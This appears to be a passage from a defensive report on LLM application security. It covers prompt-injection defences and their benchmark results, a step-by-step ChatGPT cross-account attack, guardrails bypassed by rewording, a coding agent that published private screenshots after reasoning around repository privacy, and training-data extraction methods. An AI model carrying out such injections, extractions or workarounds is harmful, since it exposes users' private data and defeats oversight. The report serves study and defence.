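| Ordinary agent with policies | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| FIDES with policies | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

The paper's headline result, that FIDES completes 8% more tasks than a basic agent, refers to the second row. FIDES's completion rate was 16 to 46 percentage points lower than that of an agent with no protection. Its lead over the policy-bound agent doubled with OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model.

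In many of the lost tasks, the user wants the agent to follow someone else's text. For example, when the agent has to pay a bill according to instructions in a file, reading the file makes the conversation untrusted, so FIDES blocks the payment. It cannot distinguish an honest bill from a forged one. Other tasks failed because GPT-4o confused variables or read untrusted data that it did not need. FIDES also permits some harm, since an email can still make the quarantined model write an empty or misleading summary.

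### Plans with branches and teams of agents

CaMeL's guarantee covers one agent, but newer products often divide work among several. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a team of three agents, each protected by CaMeL and running GPT-5.2. The user asked the lead agent to send a colleague a summary of job applicants' details. One database record contained an instruction to email the data to an outside address.

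The database agent and the lead agent both kept to their plans. But the lead agent pasted the summary into its request to the messaging agent, whose privileged model treated the whole request as coming from its user and added a step that emailed the data out. Peters-Gill and colleagues prove that any such team can fail this way if it reads untrusted data and its agents can pass results to one another freely.

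Like a parameterised query, their fix puts instructions and data in separate fields of each request between agents. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's result. They compared the versions on their multi-agent AgentDojo, with 949 attacks per model and no policies beyond the fixed plans.

| Model | No CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | With separate data field |
|---|---|---|---|
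| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0% | 0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0% | 0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | 0% | 0% |

On a second benchmark, of industrial maintenance tasks, putting CaMeL in each agent reduced task completion by an average of 21.6 percentage points. The loss was 13.4 points for the two strongest models, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. The separate data field lowered completion by another 3.2 points on average. Most failures arose because the program was finalized too early. Sometimes the need for another step became clear only after a result came back. In other cases, an agent could not find data for the requested dates and returned data for nearby dates, and the program continued unchanged.

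The separation also depends on software that can have bugs. Peters-Gill and colleagues acknowledge that CaMeL's interpreter can lose track of where a value came from when untrusted data decides which part of a program runs, and that their version has the same problem.

Even with a perfect interpreter, an attacker has some influence over which branch of a plan an agent takes. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) adapts CaMeL to agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen. A fake button on a web page cannot add a new action, but it may lead the agent into a dangerous branch that the plan already contains. *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) presents COBRA, a system that sets limits for each branch. Of the 86 tasks that both systems attempted, COBRA completed 36 and the earlier system completed 22.

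CaMeL also detects a forbidden action only when the program reaches it. Nikolaou and colleagues address this weakness with a tool that analyses the finished plan before any step runs. The tool can enforce rules about the order of steps, such as requiring an agent to get approval before disconnecting a computer from the network. If a plan breaks a rule, the tool returns the steps that break it so that the model can repair the plan. The tool may reject some safe plans because it considers every path through a loop, including paths that would never occur.

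### Testing the controls

Developers can test most controls in application code without a language model by replacing its output with fixed text. A bold tag sent to the chat page should appear as visible characters. A template expression that multiplies 7 by 7 should not turn into 49. The query for customer 18's address should return no rows when customer 17 is signed in. A tool call to an internal address should fail both in the application and at the firewall. These tests give the same result every time and stay valid when the company changes models. They cover only the sinks that developers have listed, so the complete application needs testing too.

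Open-source scanners automate part of that work. Garak, which Leon Derczynski created and NVIDIA maintains, sends a model large sets of test prompts and searches the answers for warning signs, such as raw terminal control characters, invented package names and image links that could carry data. A hit shows that the model can produce such text, but the text may be harmless if the application encodes it.

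A clean scan covers only the scanner's own prompts on one version of one model, and TicketOracle showed how much models differ. A scanner that checks only the text of answers also cannot detect what a browser or database would do with them.

Testing with fixed sets of attacks also overstates how well defences work. In *AutoDojo*, Ma, Li and colleagues (2026) had a language model repeatedly rewrite injections, given only the success rates of earlier versions. Across ten defences and five models, the standard attacks often made protection look much stronger than it was, though some designs that restrict an agent's actions remained effective against the rewritten attacks. Attacks succeeded far more often when the user left the choice of action to the content, for instance by asking the agent to do whatever an email said. A test suite made up of precise requests will therefore miss much of the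 risk.

Without CaMeL, none of the 949 attacks on GPT-5.5 succeeded. That result is statistically compatible with a true success rate of up to about 0.4%, but this bound applies only to attacks like those in the benchmark. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn against reading the result as immunity, since adaptive attackers in large contests have found successful injections against every leading model tested.

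## How does output reveal private data from prompts, documents and other users, and what prevents it?

Private data in an answer may come from the developers' hidden instructions, a retrieved record, the assistant's memory of earlier conversations or another user's session. An agent may also publish its own working files. These leaks can happen without an image or link that sends data out, like the one EchoLeak relied on, and without personal data in the model's training text.

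### An order lookup with no ownership check

A real shop had almost the same fault as the imaginary kitchenware shop. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe its public chatbot, which Sumit Shah wrote about in November 2025. When a person typed a question containing an order number, the model copied the number into a tool call, and the application fetched the order with that number without checking whether the person had signed in or whose order it was.

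The chatbot gave out a customer's email address on request, then delivery addresses, including those for several orders in one message. Order numbers had a fixed prefix and six digits, so there were only a million possible numbers. Nothing limited the number of requests, so an attacker could have tried every one.

Web developers call this flaw an insecure direct object reference. The application fetches a record using an identifier supplied by the user, without checking that the user is allowed to access it. The request for the email address reads like an ordinary customer question, although Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian label it a prompt injection. The chatbot answered it as its developers had designed it to, so a model that resisted every injection would have leaked the same data.

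The remedy is to search only among the records that the current user may see. The first query below has the flaw, and the second does not:

```
SELECT * FROM orders WHERE order_id = ?
SELECT status FROM orders WHERE order_id = ? AND customer_id = ?
```

Both are parameterised, but the second also requires the customer number from the login and returns only the order's status. If the order belongs to someone else, the model receives an empty result and has no order data to reveal.

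This leak should be fixed at the lookup rather than in an output filter, because the email address in an answer looks the same whether its owner or a stranger is asking. Blocking every address would stop customers from checking their own details, and allowing addresses would let the leak through. To tell the two cases apart, the filter would need data on who is signed in and who owns the order. An application with that data can refuse the lookup in the first place.

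The filter would also have to recognise everything private in an order. It might catch the address but miss a sentence saying that the customer bought a pregnancy test. By the time it runs, the record is already in the context, where it can influence a later answer or end up in a log.

Limiting the number of requests and using long random order numbers would have slowed an attacker down, but neither replaces the ownership check, as a second chatbot shows. The security company Tenable (2026) found that Yuma AI's Chat AI, which several online shops have built into their sites, would reveal a customer's purchases and shipping address to anyone who gave an order number or the customer's email address. It did not require them to sign in. Many people may know a customer's email address, so random order numbers would not have protected these customers. Tenable's advisory lists no known solution.

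Some shops let people order without an account, so there is no login to check. The application can instead email a one-time code to the address on the order and look up the order only after the person enters the code. The application has to check the code itself, because a model might accept a persuasive excuse in place of the code.

### Why OWASP widened "system prompt leakage"

The system prompt is the hidden instructions that developers place at the start of the context. OWASP's 2025 list had an entry for leaks of this prompt, which the 2026 edition renamed Hidden Context Exposure. According to Invicti, the old name suggested that an attacker learns only the instructions. The new entry also covers descriptions of the available functions, company policies retrieved from documents or configuration stores, and anything else in the context that the user does not see. SC Media's *OWASP updates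 top 10 security risks for LLM applications* links the revised list to the growing use of agents and retrieval-augmented generation, both of which add such material.

A model can repeat, summarise or translate any of this text. A filter that searches answers for sentences from the system prompt will miss a French paraphrase.

OWASP treats the exposure as harmful mainly because it helps other attacks. Suppose the shop instructs the model to approve refunds below 50 euros without review. A customer who learns this can ask for 49 euros. An attacker who sees a function description for changing a delivery address knows which tool call to target. The severity ranges from trivial to critical, and is critical when the disclosed details help an attacker run code or remove data on a large scale. If the context contains a password, disclosing it is harmful in itself.

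Invicti quotes OWASP as advising that "any contents of the context should not be considered a secret". The automated attacks on secrets described earlier support this, since they eventually beat every defence that relied on the model.

Developers can usually follow the advice without losing a feature. If the chatbot needs a key to contact a delivery company, the key can stay in the application's settings. The model's tool call contains the function name and the parcel number, and the application adds the key when it sends the request. If the application itself enforces the refund rules, a customer who discovers the 50-euro limit gains little. The application can still search each answer for known keys before the user sees it, in case somebody has pasted one into a document.

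Written rules about personal data are a weaker measure because the model may not follow them, as OWASP's *LLM02:2025 Sensitive Information Disclosure* warns. Android Developers' *Prevent sensitive information disclosure*, Google's guidance for app makers, still includes a sample instruction forbidding the model to share any user details under any circumstances. This rule would be wrong for the kitchenware shop even if the model always followed it, because a customer may reasonably ask where her own parcel is going.

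Unlike passwords, personal data often has to be in the context because a useful answer requires it. The shop can't leave out the customer's address when she asks about her delivery. But it can limit the context to what she is entitled to see, so that even an answer that repeats all of it reveals nothing she shouldn't have.

### Retrieved documents

Before anyone asks a company assistant a question, a program has usually split each of the company's files into passages, converted each passage into a list of numbers that represents its meaning, and stored the lists in an index. When an employee asks a question, the application converts it in the same way and retrieves the passages whose lists are most similar to the question's.

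The index is a copy, so it does not automatically keep the permissions on the original files. If it includes a salary spreadsheet and the application searches with its own account, the application is again a confused deputy, and any employee who asks about pay may receive a colleague's salary.

To prevent this, developers can store a list of permitted users or groups with each passage and exclude the passages a user isn't permitted to see before the search ranks the rest. Removing forbidden passages after the ranking is just as secure but gives worse answers. If the search returns only the ten best matches and all of them are forbidden, the model receives no passages, even if the eleventh was permitted and would have answered the question.

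Copied permissions also go out of date. An index that updates its permissions once a night can keep serving a file for hours after someone has lost access to it. Saved answers have the same problem, so if the application saves a summary of a restricted file for reuse, the summary needs the file's restrictions too.

An access check applies a company's existing permissions, including the mistaken ones. For example, someone may have accidentally shared a folder with the entire staff years ago. This did little harm when people had to know where to look for the folder, but an assistant that searches by meaning can reveal its contents in response to an innocent question. Companies therefore need to review their file permissions before connecting an assistant.

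### Memory and the right recipient

Some assistants store facts from one conversation and add them to the context of later ones. This saves users from repeating themselves, but it also means a successful attack can expose more private data. Tenable's *HackedGPT* reports seven vulnerabilities and attack techniques in ChatGPT, some of which could let an attacker steal private information from a user's stored memories.

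An assistant's memory can also leak private data with no attacker involved. Suppose a user once told her assistant about medical treatment. Months later she asks it to write to her manager to move a meeting, and the draft explains that she has a hospital appointment. An access check would not stop this, because the data is hers and she made the request, even though the email is going to her manager.

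In privacy research, contextual integrity is the idea that whether information should be shared depends on its recipient and purpose as well as its type. For example, a person's doctor should have medical details that their manager usually should not. To test this, people can label which stored facts a task needs and which its recipient should not get, then give a model the facts and the task, with the recipient named. The test has to count both the unsuitable facts the model includes and the necessary facts it leaves out, because if it counted only the first, an assistant that wrote empty emails would get a perfect score.

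A developer can reduce the risk by storing memories in separate groups and loading only the relevant one, so that a work email draws on facts about work. This will sometimes leave out a fact the user wants to include, as when she wants her manager to know about the treatment. If the system shows her the draft before sending it and she reads it, she can remove private facts or add missing ones.

### Leaks between users

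The simplest leak between users comes from a cache, which stores recent answers so they don't have to be generated again. If the shop files each answer under the question alone, the second customer to ask "Where is my order?" gets the first customer's answer. Filing each answer under both the question and the customer's account prevents this.

Press reports in September 2026 described a less obvious shared component in ChatGPT, found by researchers at the security company Check Point. ChatGPT runs the programs it writes in containers, isolated environments that are supposed to keep users apart. In January, Willison (2026) had noted in *What we learned today about this ChatGPT “container” environment* that programs in a container could not make general internet requests, but package installers could fetch software through internal proxies. According to medianet's *Sicherheitslücke in ChatGPT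 entdeckt* (2026), containers belonging to different accounts used the same internal service, an installation of JFrog's package store Artifactory. Any container could attach notes to an item in the store and read notes left by others.

eSecurity Planet's *ChatGPT Flaw Let Attackers Secretly Hijack a Victim’s AI Session* (2026) describes how this became an attack:

1. The attacker gets an instruction into the victim's conversation. The victim might paste a prompt from elsewhere, open a shared conversation or use a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that another user has configured.
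2. The attacker leaves a task in the notes on the package store.
3. The victim sends an ordinary message. ChatGPT answers it, but also reads the task and carries it out with the victim's permissions.
4. ChatGPT writes the result back to the notes, where the attacker's own session collects it.

In the demonstration, ChatGPT fetched email data from the victim's connected Gmail account, but the victim saw a normal answer. According to medianet, the only clue was a label beside the answer, and the system recorded the label after the email had been read.

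An output filter on the visible answer would have found nothing wrong. Blocking outside addresses would not have helped either, because the data went from one account to another inside OpenAI's systems. Check Point calls the method "coerced insider", according to TechRadar's *A worrying ChatGPT bug let strangers read Gmail messages*. The fix has to be in the shared service. OpenAI could have given each account its own copy, or let containers read packages but not write anything. It has since retired the Artifactory installation.

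This was the second flaw in the same isolation that Check Point disclosed in 2026. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (March 2026) describes a hidden route from the containers to the public internet, which a single malicious prompt could use to send out the user's messages and uploaded files. Check Point also told medianet that the later compromise of Hugging Face originated in the shared package service, and that Check Point had demonstrated the weakness before the compromise happened.

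Users can limit the damage from such flaws by disconnecting services they do not need. eSecurity Planet also recommends ChatGPT's "Always ask" setting, which requires approval before a connected app performs an action. A request to open Gmail during an unrelated conversation might have made the victim suspicious.

### Agents that publish their work

Coding agents have exposed private data without any attacker. *PixelLeak*, a report by the security company Glow (September 29, 2026), describes more than 13,000 internal images from over 300 organisations that were publicly available on GitHub.

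Each case that Glow investigated began with a routine job. A developer asked an agent to change a program's appearance and show the reviewers screenshots. GitHub lets people attach images to a proposed code change in a web browser, but the agents worked through a command-line program that could not do this. They instead put the screenshots in a public repository, where the reviewers and anyone else could see them.

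Glow reproduced the leak using Anthropic's Claude Code with the Opus 5 model and a private repository for a Minesweeper game. The agent's reasoning included the facts that the repository was private and that images stored there would appear broken to the reviewers. The agent then created a public repository for the images, treating privacy as a technical obstacle. Glow describes only this run, which explains how the leak occurs but not how often an agent would choose the same solution.

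The published images included billing records that a large manufacturer held for a utility company, and a financial firm's internal screens for moving money. At one software vendor, more than a dozen agents saved the workaround as a skill to use on every development task. They uploaded over a thousand screenshots and recordings, and summaries of features that were weeks or months from release. Around a third of the organisations had developers running gitshot, a small tool that publishes screenshots for code review. Both agents and people can run gitshot, so a person may have chosen to publish some of the images.

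Companies had trouble noticing the images because 93% of the time they were in a repository under an employee's own username, outside the company's GitHub account. Scanners that search repositories for sensitive data also read only text, not images. screenpipe's *ScreenLeak* introduces a benchmark for removing personal data from screen recordings and screenshots, which it describes as the first.

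Defences against prompt injection don't address PixelLeak, because the agents were following their users' instructions. A filter on the agents' replies would have found only a harmless-looking link. Restricting agents' ability to publish would be more effective. An agent whose GitHub key works only in the company's own repositories cannot create a repository under the employee's name. The company can also require a person to approve anything before it becomes public, and it should give agents a private way to share images, since the reviewers needed them.

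An attacker can provoke the same kind of publication. The Next Web's *‘GitLost’* reports that researchers at the security firm Noma posted a fake request in an organisation's public repository, where an AI agent from GitHub handled incoming issues. The agent read a file from one of the organisation's private repositories and posted its contents in public. GitHub had set up guardrails against this, but the researchers got past them by slightly changing the wording. If the agent had only had access to public files, it would have had nothing private to post.

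AI coding assistants can also expose secrets by writing passwords and keys into code that becomes public. OECD's *AI Coding Assistants Drive Surge in Secret Leaks on GitHub* (2026), an entry in the organisation's record of AI incidents, classes this as actual and continuing harm, though an AI system wrote that assessment.

### How filters recognise private data

Some of these leaks do pass through text that a program can inspect. Such programs combine several methods.

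A pattern describes the shape of the data. This one matches four groups of four digits:

```
[0-9]{4} [0-9]{4} [0-9]{4} [0-9]{4}
```

A filter with a pattern for payment card numbers written with spaces will miss the same numbers written with hyphens or in words. It will also match a serial number in the same format.

A checksum removes many of the false matches. The Luhn algorithm determines the last digit of a card number from the others. To check a number, the program starts from the right, doubles every second digit, subtracts 9 from any result above 9, and adds everything up. The total for a valid number is a multiple of 10. For 4111 1111 1111 1111, a number that shops use for testing, the doubled digits become one 8 and seven 2s, which make 22. The other eight digits add 8, so the total is 30 and the number passes. A random number passes one time in ten. Names, street addresses and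 most telephone numbers have no checksum.

Credentials are easier to find when their issuer gives them a fixed prefix. For keys without one, a scanner can measure how random the characters look. This check can raise false alarms, because programs contain many harmless strings that look random, such as the hashes in a lock file. It can also miss short passwords made from ordinary words.

Named-entity recognition uses a trained model to label the words in a sentence as people, places, organisations and so on. The model uses the surrounding words to distinguish a customer named Paris from the city. It makes more mistakes with text that has no capital letters, and with names and languages that were rare in its training data.

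A second language model can judge whether an answer leaks private data if the developer gives it the answer, the rules and, ideally, the recipient's identity. It can detect that "the only dentist in the village" identifies someone, which no pattern would find. However, it is slower and more expensive than pattern matching, it receives the private data itself, and text in the answer can manipulate it. The application supplies the recipient's identity and could have used it to withhold the record.

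### When most alarms are false

A detector's recall is the share of answers containing personal data that it flags, and its precision is the share of its flags that are correct. OWASP and Android Developers both recommend pattern matching but give neither figure for it. Even a detector with high recall can have low precision when personal data is rare.

Suppose an assistant gives 1,000,000 answers, of which 0.1% contain personal data. A filter catches 95% of these and wrongly flags 1% of the clean answers.

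| | Personal data | No personal data | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Flagged | 950 | 9,990 | 10,940 |
| Not flagged | 50 | 989,010 | 989,060 |
| Total | 1,000 | 999,000 | 1,000,000 |

Only 950 of the 10,940 flags (8.7%) are correct. If the application blocks every flagged answer, it refuses more than ten harmless answers for each one it correctly blocks. If people review the flags at one a minute, they need about 182 hours. Either way, the 50 missed answers still get through.

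Precision depends heavily on how common personal data is. If the same filter runs on a customer service chatbot where 10% of answers contain personal data, it catches 95,000 of them and wrongly flags 9,000 other answers, so 91% of its flags are right. It also misses 5,000, a hundred times as many as before. A supplier's precision figure from a test set full of names and card numbers is therefore a poor guide to the filter's precision in an application where such data seldom appears.

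In the first example, reducing false alarms matters more than raising recall. Perfect recall would raise precision to only 9.1%. If the filter instead wrongly flagged 0.1% of clean answers, it would produce 999 false alarms and precision would be 49%. Developers can reduce false alarms by requiring a second detector to flag the same answer. If it had the same error rates and made its mistakes independently, the pair would flag about 100 clean answers and catch about 903 of the 1,000 that contain personal data. Precision would be 90%, but the number of missed answers would almost double to 97. Real detectors tend to make mistakes on the same text, so the improvement would be smaller.

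Even a correct flag in this example means only that an answer contains personal data. Many of these answers will give customers their own details, at their request.

### Where to put the protection

| Control | What it prevents | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Access check before retrieval | Records that the user may not see | Permitted data that goes to the wrong recipient |
| Separation of users | Data passing between accounts | Leaks within one account |
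| Redaction before the model | Exposure of details that the task does not need | Data that the detector overlooks |
| Output filter | Recognisable data in text about to reach a reader | Paraphrases, pictures and channels it does not inspect |

The access check and the separation of users depend on who owns a record or session, which the application can look up exactly. They avoid the base-rate problem because they do not have to recognise private data. Android Developers points out that an attacker cannot trick a model into revealing a database the model cannot access.

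Redaction before the model suits tasks in which the identity of a person makes no difference. If the shop wants a summary of complaints, the application can replace each customer's details first:

```
[NAME_1] of [ADDRESS_1] says that the kettle leaks.
```

The model can summarise the text with placeholders as well as the original. The application keeps a private list of what each placeholder stands for and can restore the names for staff who may see them. OWASP recommends this kind of replacement before processing. It relies on the same fallible detectors as an output filter, but a false alarm hides one harmless word from the model, whereas one in an output filter may block an entire answer.

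If an injection has made the model write a placeholder into an image address, an application that replaces every placeholder with the real name will put that name in the address and send it to the attacker. The application should restore names only in visible text, and only for readers with permission to see them.

An output filter is still useful as a last check for data that should never appear in any answer, such as the company's own keys. It must cover tool calls and uploaded files as well as chat replies, and run somewhere the attacker does not control. Android Developers suggests redacting answers inside the app before it displays them. This can prevent accidental disclosure to honest users, but an attacker using the app controls the phone and can read the server's reply before the app redacts it.

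## Why do models repeat their training data, and how is this measured?

The leaks described so far came from data that an application had fetched, stored or placed in the context. A model can also repeat text from its training data to a user who supplied none of it. No access check can withhold that text, because the model's weights are one large set of numbers, with no separate record for each person or document.

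### How training stores particular passages

During training, a program adjusts the model's weights to reduce the loss, a number that is high when the model gives the actual next token in a passage a low probability. Carlini, Tramèr and colleagues (2020) point out in *Extracting Training Data from Large Language Models* that, by this measure, the ideal model would have memorised what follows every passage in its training data.

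A model lowers its loss mostly by learning patterns that apply to many texts, such as grammar. These patterns do not predict the digits of a customer's phone number, so the loss on that number falls substantially only if the weights encode it. Training adjusts the weights towards the number each time it appears in the data, so the model is especially likely to memorize repeated text.

Large models can memorise passages of their training text even when, on average, they predict that text hardly any better than new text. For GPT-2, which OpenAI released in 2019, the loss was only about 10% lower on training text. Many researchers once assumed from such small differences that large models would not memorise much, but a model can predict a few passages almost perfectly without changing its average loss much. *Probabilistic "Copies" in Generative AI Models* (2026) cites estimates that models memorise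 between 0.1% and 10% of their training sequences.

A model has memorised a piece of text when its weights encode it, and the text is extracted when the model reproduces it in its output. Cooper (2026) draws this distinction in *Playing Whack-a-Mole with misconceptions about memorization, extraction, and copyright* and notes that some memorised text cannot be extracted.

### The 50-token test

Researchers usually measure memorisation by attempting extraction. The standard test has four steps:

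1. Take 100 tokens of text from the training data.
2. Give the model the first 50 as a prompt.
3. Let it generate 50 more, choosing the most probable token each time. This is called greedy decoding.
4. Count a success only if all 50 match the original exactly.

According to *Extracting books from production language models* (Ahmed, Cooper and colleagues, 2026), AI companies also use this test in their reports on new models. The test suits models that simply continue a text, but a chatbot may reply to the passage instead. It also misses near-verbatim copies. *Estimating near-verbatim extraction risk in language models with decoding-constrained beam search* (2026) notes that most earlier work required an exact match, so a copy with one changed comma would not count.

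Fifty tokens are about 37 words, according to Cooper, but the number depends on the text. In *Quantifying Memorization Across Neural Language Models*, Carlini, Lee and colleagues (2022) counted an average of 25 words per 50 tokens in a dataset that included code. The threshold is meant to rule out coincidence. In *Scalable Extraction of Training Data from (Production) Language Models*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2023) looked for chance overlaps in news articles newer than the largest training datasets. Apart from direct quotations, they found none longer than 25 tokens, and they doubled that length to be safe.

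Cooper, Swanberg and colleagues (2026) measured how often shorter matches wrongly suggest memorization in *Extractable Memorization From First Principles*. They tested OLMo 2 32B, a model with public training data, on 5,000 Wikipedia passages from its training data and 5,000 from entries dated after its training cutoff. The table shows how often the model continued a passage exactly.

| Length of match | Training passages | Later passages |
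|---|---|---|
| 10 tokens | 7.54% | 1.84% |
| 50 tokens | 0.74% | 0.04% |

At 10 tokens, the rate for later passages is about a quarter of the rate for training passages, so a study that tested only training text would count many lucky guesses as memorisation. At 50 tokens, almost all of these guesses disappear. The 0.04% comes from a single match, and that text turned out to be in the training data.

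A long match between a model's output and its training data is not evidence of memorisation if the prompt contains the same text. When Cooper, Swanberg and their colleagues asked a chat version of OLMo to repeat passages given in the prompt, it copied text it had not been trained on as reliably as training text. They also tested a method that uses a program to search for a prompt that makes the model produce a chosen sentence. Earlier researchers had used this method to produce a quotation from the hockey player Wayne Gretzky and treated their success as evidence of memorisation. The same method made Llama 2 13B produce a remark that a basketball player made in 2026, long after the model was trained.

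Cooper raises a similar objection to a study of books that counted five-word matches and gave the models detailed summaries of the passages they were supposed to reproduce. Running the same procedure on text that cannot have been in the training data would show how much of such a result comes from coincidence or from copying the prompt. If an extraction attempt fails, the model may still have memorized the text, since another prompt might work.

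### The chance of success over many attempts

Greedy decoding always gives the same answer to the same prompt. Most chatbots instead choose tokens partly at random, so a passage may appear on some attempts and not on others. The probability that one attempt reproduces a 50-token passage is the product of the probabilities of its tokens, each given the text before it:

```
p = p1 × p2 × p3 × ... × p50
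```

This product shrinks quickly. If every token has a probability of 90%, the whole passage has a probability of about 0.5% (Cooper, Lemley and colleagues, 2025, *Extracting memorized pieces of (copyrighted) books from open-weight language models*). Researchers can calculate this probability without generating any text, by feeding the model the true passage and reading off the probability of each token. They need access to those token probabilities, which many commercial chatbots do not provide.

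Hayes, Swanberg and colleagues (2024), in *Measuring memorization in language models via probabilistic extraction*, use p to work out the risk over repeated attempts. One attempt fails with probability 1 − p, so n independent attempts all fail with probability (1 − p)^n. The rest is the chance of at least one success:

```
P(at least one success) = 1 − (1 − p)^n
```

If the chance p of producing a passage on one attempt is 1%, 100 attempts have a 63% chance of producing it at least once. For a 95% chance, the number of attempts n must be at least log(0.05) / log(0.99), which rounds up to 299. One success among hundreds of failures can be enough for an attacker who can check a phone number or card number elsewhere.

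Hayes and colleagues give an example that the standard test misses. With greedy decoding, a model reproduced the first 36 tokens of a passage. The next correct token was only the second most likely, so the model output a different one and the rest of the text diverged. With random sampling, the same model had a 16.2% chance of producing the entire passage, or about one in six attempts.

Some memorised passages are far less likely to appear. In the 2026 study by Cooper and colleagues, a probability of 10^−21 could be evidence that a model had memorised a passage from a book, because comparable text outside the training data never reached that probability. At a thousand attempts per second, reaching a 95% chance of seeing such a passage would take nearly seven times the age of the universe. The team proposes calling text "extractably memorized" only if it passes this comparison and is almost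 certain to appear within a realistic number of attempts. They add that a different decoding method can recover some low-probability text with about as much computation as generating 20 samples. The formula therefore gives the risk for one prompt and one way of choosing tokens, and a better attack may need fewer attempts.

### What the early attacks recovered

Carlini, Tramèr and their colleagues gave the first large demonstration of a model repeating its training data, using GPT-2. They generated 600,000 samples and ranked them by signs of memorisation, such as GPT-2 assigning the text a much higher probability than a smaller model did. They inspected 1,800 candidates and, with OpenAI's help, confirmed that 604 contained memorised training text. Of these, 46 contained the names of people who were not in the news and 32 contained contact details, half of them for private individuals. One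 sample contained a person's name, address, email address, phone number and fax number. Some of the recovered text was no longer on the web pages it came from.

The team also tested web addresses that appeared different numbers of times in a single training document. The largest version of GPT-2 produced every address that appeared at least 33 times, while the smallest produced none without extra hints. A model can therefore leak a string even if only one training document contains it.

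Two years later, Carlini and colleagues measured three influences on memorisation, using the GPT-Neo models and their public training data.

- **Model size.** A tenfold increase in size raised the share of passages that the model completed exactly by 19 percentage points.
- **Repetition.** The more often a passage occurred in the training data, the more likely the model was to reproduce it.
- **Prompt length.** The largest model completed 33% of passages after a prompt of 50 tokens and 65% after 450.

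To check whether larger models were simply better at guessing, the team gave the same passages to GPT-2, which was trained on different data. GPT-2 completed about 6% of them, compared with 40% for a GPT-Neo model of similar size. These percentages are higher than the overall rate because the sample deliberately included many repeated passages. The team estimated that the largest model had memorised at least 1% of the whole dataset.

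*Mitigating Memorization In Language Models* (2024) also reports that larger models memorise more, and that models trained on bigger datasets memorise less. Nasr and colleagues found that models trained for longer leaked more. These results need not conflict, since adding new text is different from training for longer on the same text.

Nasr and colleagues also attacked a deployed chatbot, the version of ChatGPT based on GPT-3.5. It seemed safe at first, since only 0.02% of the tokens it generated were part of 50-token sequences that matched text in the researchers' nine-terabyte collection of web data. They then found an unusual kind of prompt that made it stop responding conversationally and produce training text about 150 times as often. For $200 they recovered more than 10,000 different passages, the longest over 4,000 characters. Of 15,000 outputs they checked for personal data, 16.9%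 contained memorised personal details. The attack was specific to that model, and the team told OpenAI about it three months before publication.

This experiment also shows that the standard test can miss most of what a chatbot has memorized. The team took the 1,000 longest passages that the attack had recovered and prompted ChatGPT with the beginning of each. It completed only 3.5% of them, although its weights encoded them all. Training it to behave as a chat assistant had made the text harder to extract but had not removed it.

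### Personal data from fine-tuning

Companies often fine-tune a model by continuing its training on a smaller dataset of their own, which may contain customer conversations or medical records. Furukawa and Oprea (2026), in *Reconstruction of Personally Identifiable Information from Proprietary Data in Supervised Fine-Tuned Models*, tested whether such data could leak. They added invented personal details to medical and legal conversations, fine-tuned a seven-billion-parameter model on them, and tried to recover details about particular people using the model's token probabilities.

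In the medical data, an attacker who knew only a person's name and made 50 guesses at each detail found the right email address 15.9% of the time, the right city 15.7% of the time, and the right date of birth 0.2% of the time. An attacker who had the rest of the person's record, with the personal details removed, found the right email address 19.9% of the time and the right date of birth 2.5% of the time.

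Some of these successes are guesses, since many email addresses contain the owner's name. Furukawa and Oprea therefore also ran the attack on the original model. Fine-tuning raised the chance of finding the right email address in the first five guesses by 2 to 7 percentage points, depending on what the attacker knew. That increase is a better measure of the leak than the success rates themselves.

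Szep, Marin Ruiz and colleagues (2026), in *Unintended Memorization of Sensitive Information in Fine-Tuned Language Models*, fine-tuned models to write follow-up plans from real German hospital discharge summaries, so the patients' names appeared in the input but not in the answers the models had to learn. How often a name appeared explained less than 24% of the variation in how often the model produced it. Repetition seems to matter less here than in the GPT-Neo experiments, perhaps because the most frequent names were in page headers irrelevant to the task.

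Later fine-tuning can also bring back details that a model no longer gives when asked. Li, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Sleeping Secrets*, trained six small models on pairs of names and email addresses from the published archive of the energy company Enron, then on unrelated text until they recalled fewer of the addresses. Further fine-tuning on data that contained no real private records raised recovery by 6 to 21 percentage points. In one comparison, recovery rose from 42% to 63% in a model that had seen the addresses but did not rise in a matching model that had never seen them. A company that tests a model before release cannot assume that the result will hold after a customer fine-tunes it.

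The evidence on passwords and access keys is less direct. GPT-2 reproduced random strings of up to 87 characters, each from a single document, and ChatGPT produced an exact bitcoin address, so models can store text of this kind. But Li and colleagues' attack worked much less well on random answers than on ones resembling ordinary email addresses. In any case, a company should replace a key that has entered a training set, which makes the memorised copy useless, but a date of birth can't be replaced.

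### Removing duplicates and personal data

Because repetition encourages memorisation, developers commonly remove duplicate text before training. This takes some computing time but does not change the training method. Carlini, Lee and their colleagues found memorised passages that had only a few duplicates, so removing duplicates is not a complete remedy. OpenAI had removed duplicate documents from GPT-2's training data, but web addresses repeated within one document remained.

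Nasr and colleagues tested Pythia models trained with and without duplicate removal, so their results compare the two directly. The table shows the share of generated tokens that were part of memorised passages, and the number of different memorised 50-token passages in a billion tokens of output.

| Model | Memorised share | Different passages |
|---|---|---|
| Pythia 1.4B | 0.453% | 811,384 |
| Pythia 1.4B, duplicates removed | 0.578% | 837,582 |
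| Pythia 6.9B | 0.548% | 1,281,172 |
| Pythia 6.9B, duplicates removed | 0.596% | 1,313,758 |

The versions without duplicates leaked slightly more overall, though removing duplicates may still protect the passages that used to be repeated.

Removing personal data before training is more reliable for the details it catches, since a model cannot memorise a phone number that was never in its training data, but it depends on the same imperfect detectors as an output filter. The GPT-2 team calls it a first line of defence and also recommends choosing sources carefully. Much of the personal data they recovered came from sites known for hosting it, including Pastebin, an anonymous text-sharing site that was the twelfth most common domain in GPT-2's training data.

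Developers can often remove names from fine-tuning data with little loss of usefulness. A patient's follow-up plan, for example, does not depend on the patient's name. The example answers in this data deserve particular attention because, as Furukawa and Oprea explain, standard fine-tuning directly rewards a model for reproducing them, while personal data in the user's question has only an indirect effect.

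### Differential privacy and unlearning

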